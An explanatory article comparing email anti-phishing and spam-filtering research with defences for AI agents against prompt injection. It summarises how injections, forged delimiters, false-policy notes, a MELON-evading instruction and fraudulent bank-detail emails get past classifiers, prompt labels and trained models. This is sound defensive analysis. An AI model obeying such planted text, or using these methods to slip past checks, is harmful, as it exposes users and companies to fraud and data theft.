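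The researchers had another model repeatedly rewrite each injection to get past the defence. This raised the success rate against DRIFT from 7.1% to 28.5% on one model, Qwen3-235B, but had a negligible effect on ROPE, because ROPE's check ignores wording. Attacks that spread their goal over several steps never succeeded against ROPE on any of the three models tested.

The researchers also tested ROPE with fixed rules in place of the router, and the results show why the second question matters. When ROPE accepted any value from the agent's surroundings, attacks succeeded 30.6% of the time. When every value had to come from the user's request, the attacks failed, but the agent finished only 18.3% of its tasks.

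The router is a weak point. In the main tests, the router was Claude Opus 4.8, which rarely loosened the default rules. With Gemini 3 Flash instead, the attack success rate rose to 5.8%. The rate fell to zero when routers were forbidden to loosen any default, but with the cheaper routers the agent then finished only 15% to 18.3% of its tasks.

Across two benchmarks, 51 of the standard attacks got through:

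- In 23 cases the harm was in the agent's reply to the user, such as a recommendation for the attacker's hotel. ROPE checks only tool calls.
- In 21 cases the agent sent harmful content to a permitted recipient. In one, the user asked for an article summary to go to a colleague, and the agent sent the colleague a phishing link from the article as well.
- In 7 cases the user had left a sensitive value entirely to text that an attacker could write.

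ROPE also blocks legitimate tasks. One user asked an agent to fetch an electricity bill and pay it. The payee's account number appeared only in the bill, which anyone could have tampered with, so ROPE blocked the payment. When no attack was present, ROPE blocked something in 96 of the failed tasks. In 83 of those, it did so because a legitimate value, like the account number, had no trusted source.

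### The supplier's new bank account

Suppose the company protects its accounts assistant with ROPE, under a rule that an account number must come from the clerk's request or the company's payment records. The clerk asks the assistant to deal with this morning's invoices, and the assistant accepts the fraudster's emailed claim that the supplier has changed banks. The new account number appears only in that email, so the code blocks the payment, whether the email was forged or came from the supplier's real mailbox. A similar rule for email recipients would have stopped the October attack, because the forwarding address appeared only in the hidden text.

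The code would also refuse a genuine change of bank. The clerk might avoid this by asking the assistant to pay Bright Paper using the details in its email. If the router accepts the supplier as a source, the code will take an account number from any email that the mail system has verified as the supplier's. It will still reject an email from a lookalike domain, but it will pay a fraudster who sends one from the supplier's own mailbox.

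DMARC would have identified the supplier's domain, which is as much as it can establish about who wrote the email. The mistake was to let the email's author decide where the money goes. A supplier can reasonably tell a customer how much it is owed, but a company that also accepts new bank details by email is trusting everyone who can get into the supplier's mailbox.

ROPE can apply such rules only if the mail system passes the verified sender to the code that checks tool calls. Ma and colleagues note that platforms provide this information unevenly. Even when it is available, the rules do not prevent false summaries.

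## Marking text as untrusted: warning banners and prompt labels

Once a mail system has identified where a message came from, ordinary code can act on that information, as ROPE's does, or the system can show it to the reader and let them decide what to do. Companies have mostly preferred to show a notice, because it is easy to add and never delays a genuine message. Developers label untrusted text for agents for much the same reasons.

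### Tags and warnings

Many organisations put the same tag on all mail from outside. Newcastle University's *External Sender Banner*, for example, appears on every outside email except those from some pre-approved senders, and reminds staff to be careful with links and attachments. Shorter versions just add "[EXTERNAL]" to the subject line. A fraudster's invoice and a real supplier's invoice both get the tag, so it can't help a clerk tell them apart. It is more useful for exposing an outsider who poses as a colleague.

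A specific warning appears only when a check has found something, such as a failed DMARC result or a suspicious link. It singles out one email, but only if the check works. For example, an invoice sent from a supplier's hacked mailbox may not trigger a warning.

### The hospital experiment

Tolsdorf, Langer and Lo Iacono (2025), in *Phishing Susceptibility and the (In-)Effectiveness of Common Anti-Phishing Interventions*, compared both kinds of notice at a German university hospital. The hospital ran two simulated phishing campaigns aimed at 7,044 staff email accounts, in January and May 2024.

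The researchers relied on login interactions rather than clicks. A login interaction meant typing into the username and password fields of a fake hospital login page and pressing the button. The system stored no passwords, so nobody knows how many of the details were real. Clicks would have overstated the danger, because with one intervention in the May campaign, only 46% of the people who clicked went on to the login step.

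The January campaign used 12 different emails and no warnings. On average, 26% of staff tried to log in, with rates from 18% to 40% depending on the email. Whether the sender's address was internal or external made no measurable difference, which suggests that few people were checking it.

In May everyone received the same offer of a voucher for the hospital cafeteria. The researchers split the staff at random into 12 groups of 587. One group got the plain email, and 16.5% of its members tried to log in. Each of the other groups got one intervention.

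| Intervention | Reduction in login interactions |
|---|---|
| External tag in the subject line | 17% (not significant) |
| Sender's display name removed | 18% (not significant) |
| External tag in the From field | 24% (not significant) |
| Warning page after clicking the link | 44% |
| External tag as a banner in the message | 53% |
| External tag in all three places | 58% |
| Links disabled | 61% |
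| Phishing warning in plain text | 80% |
| Phishing warning in colour | 83% |
| Delivery to the spam folder | 90% |
| Coloured warning, with the sender's name replaced by "untrustworthy sender address" | 94% |

The [EXTERNAL] tag more than halved login interactions when it was a banner in the message, but did little when it was only a word in the subject line or From field. The researchers suggest that the banner gave staff some context, whereas nobody had trained them to understand the bare tag. The German news site heise headlined its report "[EXTERNAL] tags do not protect against phishing", which is too simple because it leaves out the banner's effect.

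The headline is more accurate for administrative and IT staff, the group that would include an accounts clerk. No form of the tag had a significant effect on them, while the three phishing warnings cut their login interactions by 75% to 100%. Each condition included only about 100 of these staff, so the exact percentages are unreliable. The warning page's 44% came almost entirely from a mixed group that included cleaning, kitchen and technical staff.

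The comparison also makes the specific warnings look more effective than they would be in practice, because the researchers attached them to the phishing email as though a filter had already caught it. If a real filter caught only half of such emails, a warning that stops 80% of logins would prevent 40% of them overall, less than the tag banner did. A company with a filter good enough to trigger the warning could often send the email to the spam folder instead.

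Tolsdorf and colleagues regard their results as an upper bound because they tested one email at one hospital and did not put warnings on legitimate mail. Even with the best warning, about 1% of staff tried to log in, which would be about 70 people if the email reached every account. The tests also upset people. Of 530 staff who fell for a January email and answered a survey, 60% said they were at least moderately scared.

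### Warnings beside the link

A banner at the top of an email can warn the reader without showing where the danger is. In *Put Your Warning Where Your Link Is*, Petelka, Zou and Schaub (2019) asked 701 people online to check whether the links worked in ten emails, three of which contained a phishing link.

| Warning | Phishing links clicked |
|---|---|
| None | 76.67% |
| Banner at the top of the email | 44.00% |
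| Beside the link, always visible | 33.65% |
| Beside the link, when the mouse moves over it | 30.36% |
| Beside the link, always visible, original link disabled | 15.64% |
| Full page in the browser after the click | 11.78% |
| Beside the link, when the mouse moves over it, original link disabled | 8.67% |

When the researchers disabled the original link, people could continue only by clicking the true web address shown in the warning, so they had to look at the address. People who saw the banner hovered over more of the links and stayed longer on the phishing ones, apparently searching for the bad link, but often clicked it anyway.

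The task encouraged clicking, so the rates are higher than they would be in an office. It may also have made the browser page look more effective, because someone who is only checking links can stop at a full-page warning and report the link as broken.

*Restricting the Link*, by Petelka, Berens and colleagues, confirmed in a larger experiment with 1,320 people that disabling the link helps. People clicked 38.5% of phishing links when the warning disabled the original link and 49.2% when it didn't. Making people wait before they could click also helped, but five seconds worked no better than two. The restrictions also discouraged people from opening harmless links that carried a mistaken warning.

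The supplier's invoice has no link to put a warning beside, so the nearest equivalent would be a notice in the payment program, next to the box where the clerk types the new account number.

### Habituation and false alarms

People respond less to a warning the more often they see it, which psychologists call habituation. Tolsdorf and colleagues worry most about external tags, because they appear whether or not anything is wrong. An accounts clerk who deals with suppliers all day sees the tag on most emails, and nearly all of those emails are legitimate.

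Specific warnings appear less often, so they should stay effective for longer. Tolsdorf and colleagues cite a 15-month experiment at a large company in which such warnings reduced clicks by 64% to 67%. But false alarms can weaken specific warnings too. In the experiment with 1,320 people, the phishing links led to the real company's website to keep participants safe, which made the warnings look like false alarms. Afterwards, 131 participants mentioned that, within that single sitting, they had come to trust the warnings less or had clicked through later ones.

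### Banners that a sender can hide

In April 2021 the researcher Louis Dion-Marcil showed that a sender could hide an external-sender banner with a few lines of HTML and CSS (Vumetric, *Attackers can hide 'external sender' email warnings with HTML and CSS*, 2021). Many security products insert the banner into the body of the email, where the sender's formatting rules also apply to it, so a rule that makes text invisible can hide the warning.

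The sender can also replace the banner with a reassuring message. *Phishing Scammers Remove ‘External Sender’ Email Warnings Impersonating Internal Users* (Sjouwerman, 2021) notes that the same method could produce a banner stating that the email had passed a scan. Hoxhunt's *External email warning banner phish* points out that people learn to trust mail without a banner, so hiding it makes an outsider look like a colleague. In that case, the company would have been better off without banners.

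The weakness was still there three years later. Certitude's *Exploring Anti-Phishing Measures in Microsoft 365* describes how its researchers hid the notice that Outlook adds to mail from unfamiliar addresses. They turned the text and background white, but the notice still showed in the inbox preview, which ignores the sender's formatting. They also imitated the icons Outlook displays on signed and encrypted mail. In February 2024 Microsoft told them that the finding was valid but didn't need an immediate fix.

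A mail program can avoid the problem by displaying the notice outside the message area, where the sender's formatting can't affect it. *Attackers Can Hide ‘External Sender’ Email Warnings With HTML And CSS* suggests one such notice, the built-in tag in Microsoft's Exchange mail system. A sender can still put a fake notice inside the message, as Certitude did with the icons, but can't remove the real one.

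### Delimiters and spotlighting

The simplest label for an agent is a pair of delimiters, markers that software puts before and after a piece of untrusted text. The developer instructs the model never to obey anything between them. At Microsoft, Hines, Lopez and colleagues (2024) developed this idea into a family of methods in *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting*. Here is how three of them would treat a sentence from the fraudster's email.

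| Method | What the model receives |
|---|---|
| Delimiting | `<<Our bank details have changed.>>` |
| Datamarking | `Our^bank^details^have^changed.` |
| Encoding | `T3VyIGJhbmsgZGV0YWlscyBoYXZlIGNoYW5nZWQu` |

Delimiting marks only the start and end of the text, so the model may lose track of the boundary in a long email. Datamarking repeats a marker throughout the text. Encoding rewrites the text in a standard code so that it no longer looks like an instruction, but the model has to be capable enough to decode it.

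In the first tests, spotlighting cut attack success from over 50% to below 2%, according to *Prompt Injection Through Forensic Evidence* (2026). The paper adds that Hines and colleagues warned about forgery. An attacker who knows that the software uses these delimiters can put `>>` in the email, followed by a sentence that looks like the clerk's next request. The forged delimiter works like the fake banner. Software can make forgery harder by choosing a new random marker for each email.

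Google tried a similar method on an email assistant, inserting a marker every eight characters into the sender, subject and body. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) reports that it worked mainly by breaking up the tokens in phrases that trigger an attack, which made the model less likely to respond to them. Less of the benefit came from warning the model about the attack. The method would probably help less against a believable story about a new bank account, which contains no such phrase.

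### Results against fixed attacks

Recent tests of delimiters have been much less encouraging, even when the attacker doesn't try to get around them. The table gives attack success rates on five open models. The figures for gpt-oss, Llama and Qwen come from *Defense Against Indirect Prompt Injection via Tool Result Parsing* (2026). Those for Gemma and Nemotron come from *RAISED* (Dhouib, Elliker and colleagues, 2026), which used AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, banking, travel and messaging tasks. The last column shows a different defence, in which software repeats the user's request after the untrusted text.

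| Model | No defence | Delimiters | Request repeated |
|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 26.45% | 23.29% | 14.75% |
| Llama-3.1-70B | 22.23% | 13.17% | 11.80% |
| Qwen3-32B | 29.82% | 25.08% | 16.86% |
| Gemma-4-12B | 39.5% | 43.9% | 34.1% |
| Nemotron-3-Nano-30B | 11.7% | 11.4% | 6.3% |

Repeating the request did better on every model. Position may matter here as it does for people, since the repeated request comes after the hostile text and just before the model acts. But repeating the request can interfere with ordinary work. It lowered Gemma's score from 57 to 33 on a separate tool-use test that contained no attacks.

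*INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, 2026) reports larger benefits from labels. The agents worked at a computer's command line, where files and program output contained planted orders, such as uploading a private key. On a selection of tasks where the agents were most vulnerable, attacks succeeded 58.2% of the time. Delimiters that named the type of source, such as file content, cut that rate by 32.5 percentage points. Written instructions to ignore injected commands cut it to 14.3%.

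The side effects varied by model. With the written instructions, Gemini-3.1-Flash-Lite's task completion under attack rose by 42.4 points, while Gemma-3-12B's fell by 16.9. A developer therefore has to test a label on the model it will be used with.

In the mailbox study by Wu and colleagues, by contrast, labels and general instructions hardly reduced the forged-situation attack's success. The type of attack probably explains much of the difference, because Nguyen and colleagues planted orders, while the mailbox attack relied on a false account of events. *PARSE* (2026) notes that delimiters work on obvious injections but give the model no useful signal when the planted text resembles the document's own content. An email about new bank details is supposed to contain bank details, so a label marking the whole email as untrusted doesn't show the model that the number is false.

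False claims don't always succeed, either. *Prompt Injection Through Forensic Evidence* cites an experiment in which someone added comments to code stating that the code had already passed an audit. The comments did not significantly change the verdicts of eight code-reviewing models.

### Results against adaptive attacks

Prompt labels do much worse when attackers adapt their attacks. In *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), spotlighting let through as few as 1% of fixed attacks but more than 95% of adaptive ones.

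An attacker can get past a marker without forging it. *CounterSteer* (2026) tested 18 cases in which an attacker wanted to change the details of an agent's action, with 24 wordings for each, varying the tone and claimed authority. Delimiters lowered the success rate of a single attempt from about 71% to 60%, but in every case at least one wording worked, with or without them. Such a marker does little to stop an attacker who can send 24 emails or rehearse on a copy of the agent.

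Plain-language warnings also failed in *MINE* (2026), which tested an attack on Llama-3.1-70B as it answered questions about documents. The attacker planted two passages on the document's topic, one near the start and one near the end. Two defences based on prompt instructions let through 61% and 80% of the attacks. In longer documents, both let through more than 97%. The attacker had designed the passages to beat a different defence, so an attack aimed at the warnings might have succeeded more often.

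### Training a model to rank its sources

Developers can train a model to respect the labels so they don't have to explain them in every prompt. In an instruction hierarchy, the developer's instructions outrank the user's, and both outrank anything in an email or web page. The training examples include conflicts between these sources, and the model learns to follow the higher-ranking one.

Training a model to resist injections works far better than delimiters against fixed attacks, but Dhouib and colleagues found that it can also teach the model not to follow legitimate directions in tool output. In one example, a user asks an agent to change a password and to finish the job without help. The website sends a verification code, which the agent can read through its tools. The original model finds the code and enters it, but a model trained to resist injections stops and asks the user for it.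 Training had repeatedly punished that model for following directions in tool output and had seldom rewarded it for following legitimate ones.

Their own method, RAISED, tries to avoid this in three steps.

1. A copy of the model invents small tasks and solves them. Many of the tasks require it to follow legitimate directions in a tool's output.
2. The same copy writes injections and inserts them into those outputs.
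3. A second copy trains on both the clean and the injected versions, and learns to respond to each as the original model did to the clean one. Training minimises the Kullback–Leibler divergence D(q‖p), which measures how far the second copy's probabilities for the next token, p, stray from the original's, q.

The model therefore learns to ignore the injection without learning to distrust everything a tool returns. On AgentDojo, RAISED cut the success rate of attacks on Gemma from 39.5% to 1.0%. Without an attack, the share of tasks the model completed fell only slightly, from 84.5% to 83.5%. An earlier training method, SecAlign++, gave almost the same protection but reduced completion to 77.3%. Some newer models are less vulnerable to begin with. Attacks on Qwen3.8-27B succeeded 5.8% of the time before RAISED and 0.9% after it.

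Dhouib and colleagues used a fixed set of attacks and did not test an attacker who adjusts the email after seeing how the trained model responds, so a company can learn little from the 1% about how the model would handle a determined fraudster. They recommend RAISED as one layer, alongside limits on what the agent can access and do.

### Whether models get used to warnings

A model that starts each task with no memory of the last can't grow used to a label through repetition, which removes the main objection to tagging everything. The closest thing to fatigue is the effect of length. The results on long documents suggest that a warning works less well when it makes up a smaller share of what the model reads.

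Staff who see too many false alarms start to ignore the warnings, whereas a model trained too heavily to resist injections may stop acting on honest emails. An AI accounts assistant has to take amounts and due dates from suppliers' emails, all of which are untrusted text. Telling it to distrust them all is no more informative than an "External" tag, since neither separates malicious emails from honest ones.

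More specific advice helps somewhat, as the instruction to distrust unverified claims did in the mailbox study, but the model still has to decide which claims to believe.

### Notices that an attacker cannot write

Most prompt labels resemble a banner inside the message, because an agent reads them in the same stream as the attacker's text. If a security product has inserted a banner into the email, the agent's software may pass that along too, even if the sender has made it invisible to people. The model would also receive the sender's line claiming that the email passed a scan, and would have to work out which one is accurate.

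Models do have something close to a notice drawn by the mail program. Developers can reserve special marker tokens for their own software and strip any imitations from incoming text. They can also use instruction-priority embeddings. A model converts each token into a list of numbers before processing it, and these embeddings add further numbers that depend on whether the token came from the developer, the user or an outside source. A fraudster can't produce those numbers by typing text into an email.

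This prevents forgery, but the model can still give the label too little weight, as models did in the tests by Ye and colleagues. A clerk can likewise overlook a notice that Outlook displays correctly.

The clerk may also need a label on the assistant's output. When the assistant summarises the supplier's email, the banner on the original usually disappears, and the claim about the new bank account appears in the assistant's own words. The chat program could display a notice beside the summary listing the verified domain of each source email. Neither the fraudster nor the model could remove the notice, though the clerk might start to ignore it after a few weeks.

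## Filtering text before it is read

A banner or prompt label leaves the hostile text in front of the reader. A filter keeps the text from the reader, so it doesn't matter how easily it would have deceived the clerk or the agent. But hostile text is difficult to recognise. Engineers have worked on recognising spam for more than twenty years, and they gradually came to rely less on the content of messages.

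### Filtering by words

Early statistical spam filters counted words. A naive Bayes filter, the most popular kind, learns from labelled mail how often each word appears in spam and in legitimate mail. It then treats every word in a new email as a separate piece of evidence.

Suppose an email starts with even odds of being spam. A word that is eight times as common in spam as in legitimate mail raises the odds to eight to one. Two words that are each four times as common in legitimate mail bring the odds down to one to two, and the email reaches the inbox. Taking logarithms turns the multiplication into a sum:

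score = log [P(spam) / P(legitimate)] + Σ log [P(word | spam) / P(word | legitimate)]

The filter blocks the email if the score is above a threshold.

A spammer can therefore keep the sales pitch and add words that lower the score. Lowd and Meek, in *Good Word Attacks on Statistical Spam Filters*, tested this on two filters they had trained on 500,000 Hotmail messages. Random dictionary words raised the score, probably because so many spammers were already adding them. Words that were common in news articles and other everyday text but rare in spam worked much better.

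Attackers who could send test messages needed to add fewer words. They could adjust an email until it only just counted as spam, then add one dictionary word at a time and note which ones got it into the inbox. The table shows how many added words got half of the blocked spam through, with the number of test messages in brackets. The second filter used a maximum entropy model, which also adds up word weights but learns them differently.

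| Attack | Naive Bayes | Maximum entropy |
|---|---|---|
| Educated guesses | 112 (0) | 149 (0) |
| First good words found | 59 (3,083) | 20 (4,262) |
| Best good words found | 29 (61,982) | 9 (68,987) |

The maximum entropy filter missed 31% less spam when it wasn't under attack, but an attacker needed fewer words to get past it because it gave some words very large weights. A filter's accuracy on ordinary mail was a poor predictor of how well it would withstand an attack.

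Lowd and Meek considered blocking emails that contain lists of unrelated words, but a spammer can work those words into ordinary paragraphs. Making the filter's answers inconsistent only forces the attacker to send more tests. They found only frequent retraining effective. The filters blocked between 63% and almost 100% less spam under attack, and retraining them on examples of the attacks restored about their original performance. But the retrained filters were tested on the same word lists they had learned from, and a spammer with a new list would get more spam through until the next retraining.

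Virus Bulletin's *Blinding POPFile via a single-word attack* (2006) mentions spammers who also manipulated an email's HTML to hide words such as "Viagra" from filters. Hidden prompt injections do the opposite, hiding words from the person while leaving them readable to the AI agent.

### Signals that cost money to fake

*Adversarial Classification* (Dalvi, Domingos and colleagues, 2004) describes filtering as a game in which every change to a message takes effort or makes the message less useful to the sender. The sender looks for the changes that will get the message through with the least effort and loss, and makes them only if delivery is worth it. A spammer can easily reword an email, but too much rewording stops it from selling the product. A filter is therefore harder to beat if it uses features that are hard for the sender to change.

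One such feature is the network an email comes from. For *Understanding the Network-Level Behavior of Spammers*, Ramachandran and Feamster collected over 10 million spam messages in 18 months at a domain with no real users. They concluded that spammers could change a message's content far more easily than where they sent it from. About 80% of the spam came from IP addresses on at least one of eight blacklists.

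However, a blacklist that adds individual addresses after the first complaints would often be too late. Most of the infected computers that sent the spam sent fewer than 100 messages each to the domain, and about three-quarters were active only once, for less than two minutes.

SPF and DKIM let filters keep a history for each sender's domain, a more lasting identifier. *Sender Reputation in a Large Webmail Service* (Taylor, 2006) describes how one provider scored authenticated domains by their history. *The War Against Spam* (Taylor, Fingal and Aberdeen) reports that Google's mail system counted the spam and legitimate mail from each source, using its own classifications and users' clicks on "Report Spam" and "Not Spam". It sent mail from sources with very low scores straight to spam.

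Hearn (2014), who had worked on Gmail's spam team, estimated in a post to the Messaging mailing list that the reputations of the sending address and of the domains in an email's links were enough to deal with perhaps 90% of spam or more, and that analyzing the text contributed comparatively little. Addresses and domains cost money, and a spammer needs many of them.

Spammers responded by exploiting other people's reputations. They opened thousands of accounts at respected free mail services and got people to solve the puzzles meant to block automated sign-ups. Hearn (2014) recalls in *Modern anti-spam and E2E crypto* that Gmail also relied heavily on the rule that friends don't spam each other, until criminals hijacked accounts in large numbers and the rule stopped being reliable. A fraudster with access to the supplier's mailbox benefits in the same way, because years of honest invoices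 make the false one more believable.

Attacks sent in bulk are also easier to filter. The source and text of a phishing campaign against a bank's customers may change every hour, but a provider that handles many of the emails can learn from the first reports. When a fake invoice is sent to only one clerk, the provider has no earlier reports of the same attack to learn from.

Language models have since made text even easier to rewrite. In *SoK*, Chen, Wu and colleagues (2026) tested ten phishing detectors, including the widely used SpamAssassin and Rspamd. Nine did worse on phishing written by models than on phishing written by people. SecureNet, the best detector on human writing, fell from 0.78 to 0.53 on a scale where 1 is perfect and 0 is no better than chance. The messages came from different public collections, so authorship may not explain the whole difference.

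### Classifiers for prompt injection

Defenders of agents have mostly gone back to filtering text by its wording. An injection classifier is usually a small language model trained on ordinary text and known injections. It scores each email or web page before the agent's software adds it to the context, and the software blocks anything that scores above a threshold.

A developer can ask a general-purpose model whether a text contains an injection, or use a perplexity filter, which flags text to which a language model assigns a very low probability. These filters are meant to catch the gibberish strings that some automated attacks produce.

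Two other methods test what the text does to a model. DataSentinel tells a model to repeat a secret key and ignore the text that follows. If the model fails to repeat the key, it has probably followed instructions in the text instead. MELON runs the agent a second time with the user's request replaced by a harmless request for a summary. If the agent makes the same tool call in both runs, the text probably prompted it.

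OpenAI's objection, that detecting a well-made injection is as hard as detecting a lie, applies to all of these. *The Attacker Moves Second* describes an injection that got past a detector made by Protect AI. It was written as a note to the user, saying that a new company policy required anyone rescheduling a calendar event to log the change by deleting a temporary file, which it identified by number. Nothing in the note looks like an attack, so the detector would need information showing that the company has no such policy to recognise it as one.

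The supplier's invoice is even harder to filter. A genuine notice of new bank details and a fraudulent one could be identical except for the account number, so a classifier given only the text would have no basis for blocking one and passing the other. It could block both, but a company that wants to check every change of bank details can do so without a classifier.

### Ten hostile texts in a million

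Even a classifier that recognises nearly every attack can produce mostly false alarms, because attacks are rare. Suppose a company's agents read a million texts a month, ten of which are hostile. The classifier detects 99% of hostile texts and wrongly flags 0.1% of harmless ones. The table compares this classifier with an equally accurate spam filter at a company where half of the incoming mail is spam.

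| | Injection classifier | Spam filter |
|---|---|---|
| Texts per month | 1,000,000 | 1,000,000 |
| Hostile or spam | 10 | 500,000 |
| Caught | about 10 | 495,000 |
| False alarms | about 1,000 | 500 |
| Share of alerts that are correct | about 1% | 99.9% |

About ten of the injection classifier's roughly 1,010 alerts are real attacks. Someone on the security team who opened a hundred alerts would find one attack on average, and might well stop looking carefully before reaching it. For half the alerts to be correct, the false-alarm rate would have to be a hundred times lower, at about 0.001%.

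The figure of ten is invented, and the true share will vary between companies and over time. *"In vivo" spam filtering* lists skewed and changing proportions of spam and legitimate mail among the difficulties that a real spam filter faces and a laboratory test can miss. An injection classifier has the same problem in a more extreme form. A developer who tests one on a collection that is half attacks will see a high share of correct alerts, and should expect a lower share in use.

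### What a false alarm costs an agent

A spam filter can make mistakes without doing much harm because it seldom deletes email. It moves the email to a folder, which cut login attempts by 90% in the hospital experiment, and a person who is expecting the email can look for it there. Taylor and colleagues found that many Gmail users hardly ever opened their spam folders, but the clerk can still telephone a supplier whose invoice hasn't arrived.

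A filter may withhold text that the agent needs for its next step. If a classifier withholds an invoice, the software can stop the task and ask the clerk, which uses up some of the time the agent was supposed to save. If the agent carries on without the invoice, it may report that it has dealt with everything while one supplier goes unpaid. That is worse than stopping, because nobody knows an invoice is missing.

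False alarms also add up over a long task. If an agent reads 50 texts and the classifier has a 0.1% chance of wrongly flagging each one, about 5% of tasks will have at least one false alarm. At 1% per text, about 40% will.

Wang, Zou and colleagues (2026), in *AgentWatcher*, measured how classifiers affect agents when no attack is present. On the simulated office tasks in AgentDojo, the classifier PromptGuard cut an agent's score for useful work from 0.73 to 0.40. Another classifier, PIGuard, hardly affected those tasks, but it cut the score from 0.99 to 0.08 on WASP, a test of agents that use websites, where PromptGuard didn't lower the score. A classifier that works well on a company's email may therefore not work well on the web pages its agents visit.

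A less drastic response can reduce the harm from false alarms. Software could let the agent read a flagged email but stop the agent from making payments for the rest of that task. A false alarm would then delay a payment, but the agent could still do everything else.

### Twelve defences against adaptive attacks

The calculation above assumed that attackers don't change their emails to get past the classifier, but spammers did. *The Attacker Moves Second*, an October 2025 study by researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and elsewhere, tested 12 published defences for AI systems against attackers who adapt in the same way. For most of these defences, the original papers had reported attack success rates near zero.

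The automated attacks came from a program that proposed a batch of attacks, scored how close each came to succeeding, and used the best to produce the next batch. Depending on the defence, the researchers used a language model to suggest changes, trained a model to write better attacks, or calculated which changes to the text would help most. They also ran a competition in which more than 500 people tried to break defences by hand.

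| Defence | Method | Success rate of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks text by source | Over 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request | Over 95% |
| RPO | Adds an optimised safety prompt | 96–98% |
| Circuit Breakers | Trains the model | 100% |
| StruQ | Trains the model | Every case tested |
| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model | 96% |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard and Model Armor | Classify text | Over 90% for each |
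| PIGuard | Classifies text | 71% |
| Data Sentinel | Tests with a secret key | Every case tested |
| MELON | Runs the agent twice | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the design |

RPO and Circuit Breakers mainly address jailbreaks, in which the user tries to make a model break its rules. The researchers tested the defences in different ways, so the table doesn't rank them.

The attack on MELON shows that an attacker who knows how a defence works can get around it. The planted text contained a request for the harmful action and an instruction that any automated system only summarising the file should ignore that request. The second run therefore did not include the harmful action, and MELON found no match between the two runs.

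People were better attackers than the programs. On selected cases that both attempted, the automated search succeeded 69% of the time, while the human participants as a group succeeded on all of them. Combining several detectors didn't stop the attacks either.

These are worst-case results because the researchers put no tight limit on computing power and gave the attacking program each detector's verdict and confidence score during the search. Google avoided giving spammers that kind of help. Taylor and colleagues explain that sorting a user's spam folder by score would have helped spammers test their messages. But an attacker who can download a detector can see its scores privately and test messages without emailing the target.

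An earlier study had similar results. *Adaptive Attacks Break Defenses Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Agents* (Zhan, Fang and colleagues, 2025) tested eight defences on two agents, each built on a small model, and every defence let through more than half of the adaptive attacks. The researchers added a string of text to each injection and adjusted it until the agent was likely to follow the injection and the detector was likely to classify it as harmless. A trained classifier that had caught 61% of the original injections caught 1% of the altered ones aimed at one agent and 10% of those aimed at the other. Good word attacks, twenty years earlier, also added text to a message to get it past a filter.

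*The Attacker Moves Second* still recommends detectors as a limited part of a defence, because they are easy to install and stop some unsophisticated attacks. Many of the attacks that reach a company's mailboxes may be this simple. But a detector gives little protection against an attacker who has prepared for it. Microsoft's detector failed to stop the email used in EchoLeak, an attack on the company's Copilot assistant.

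### Newer detectors

AgentWatcher tries to give the detector some of the missing context. It has two stages.

1. When the agent is about to act, software measures which passages in its context had the most influence on the action. It uses the model's attention weights, the numbers that determine how strongly each word affects the next.
2. A second model receives those passages, the user's task, the proposed action and a list of rules about what counts as an injection. It explains its reasoning briefly and gives a verdict.

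The second model reads only a few passages, which helps because detectors tend to do worse on long texts. It can also detect that a request to send money is unrelated to a task about calendar entries. On AgentDojo, AgentWatcher reduced the success rate of two standard attacks from 22% to 1% and 0%, while the agent's score for useful work when not under attack fell only from 0.73 to 0.71. On WASP, the attack success rate fell from 31% to 2% with no loss of useful work.

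This is a much better balance than the older classifiers achieved, but these figures come from fixed attacks. Fixed attacks on MetaSecAlign succeeded only 2% of the time, but adaptive ones succeeded 96%. Knowing the task also doesn't help much when the lie is consistent with it. If the clerk has asked the assistant to pay the morning's invoices, the assistant should pay Bright Paper, and nothing in the task or the rules shows that the account number is wrong.

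### Detectors that an attacker can instruct

A detector built on a language model has to read the attacker's text, so the attacker can try to deceive it too. Koide, Nakano and Chiba (2026), in *Clouding the Mirror*, tested this on models that judge whether a web page is a phishing site. They made imitation login pages for ten well-known brands and planted each of 25 messages in eight places, one per page, which gave 2,000 pages. Without the messages, every model recognised every page as phishing. The researchers counted an attack as successful if the model called the page harmless, refused to answer or gave an answer that software couldn't read, since any of these would break an automated filter.

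With a simple prompt, the attacks succeeded 39.9% of the time against GPT-5 and more often against the other models. The most effective messages fooled the filter with a false explanation, such as a claim that the page belonged to a university's training course. The agents it might protect are vulnerable to the same kind of lie. These messages worked 58.3% of the time on GPT-5 and 97.3% of the time on Grok 4 Fast.

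The researchers' remedy, InjectDefuser, has three parts. It encloses the page in unpredictable markers and tells the model to treat any instruction or excuse inside them as evidence about the page. It looks up the brand's real domains in a trusted list so the model can compare them with the page's address. Finally, ordinary code checks that the answer has the right format and treats serious errors as a sign of tampering.

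The first four results columns show attack success rates. For the real sites, the researchers added their messages to 25 live phishing pages. The last column shows how many of 250 ordinary websites the protected detector misclassified as phishing.

| Model | Imitation sites, simple prompt | Imitation sites, InjectDefuser | Real sites, simple prompt | Real sites, InjectDefuser | False alarms with InjectDefuser |
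|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 39.9% | 0.3% | 52.0% | 8.9% | 1.2% |
| Grok 4 Fast | 65.1% | 26.1% | 70.2% | 25.8% | 4.4% |
| Gemma 3 27B | 64.7% | 36.7% | 67.1% | 20.4% | 25.2% |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 84.7% | 61.7% | 77.8% | 48.0% | 3.6% |

The remedy works well with GPT-5 and much less well with the others. Newer models may do better, but the 8.9% on real sites came from a fixed set of messages, and an attacker who could test messages against the detector would probably succeed more often. Gemma improved partly by rejecting pages indiscriminately, including a quarter of the ordinary websites. Even GPT-5's false alarm rate of 1.2% would mean about 12,000 false alarms in a million harmless pages.

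The list of real domains is the most useful idea here for other filters because it gives the model a fact that the attacker didn't write. Code could also compare the domains, so no excuse on the page would affect the result.

### Removing text that a person could not see

Software can also remove the parts of an email or web page where injections are hidden, without deciding whether any of the text is hostile. It works out what a mail program or browser would display and passes only that to the agent, leaving out HTML comments, elements with no size and invisible Unicode characters. In the October invoice campaign, this would have kept the instruction to forward the email from reaching any model.

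Koide and colleagues' results suggest that this is worth doing, because messages in page metadata, comments and invisible elements generally fooled the detectors more often than messages in the visible page. Ordinary code should remove them, since a persuasive sentence can't influence it. The clerk and the assistant then read the same email, so the clerk has a fair chance of noticing anything odd in a summary.

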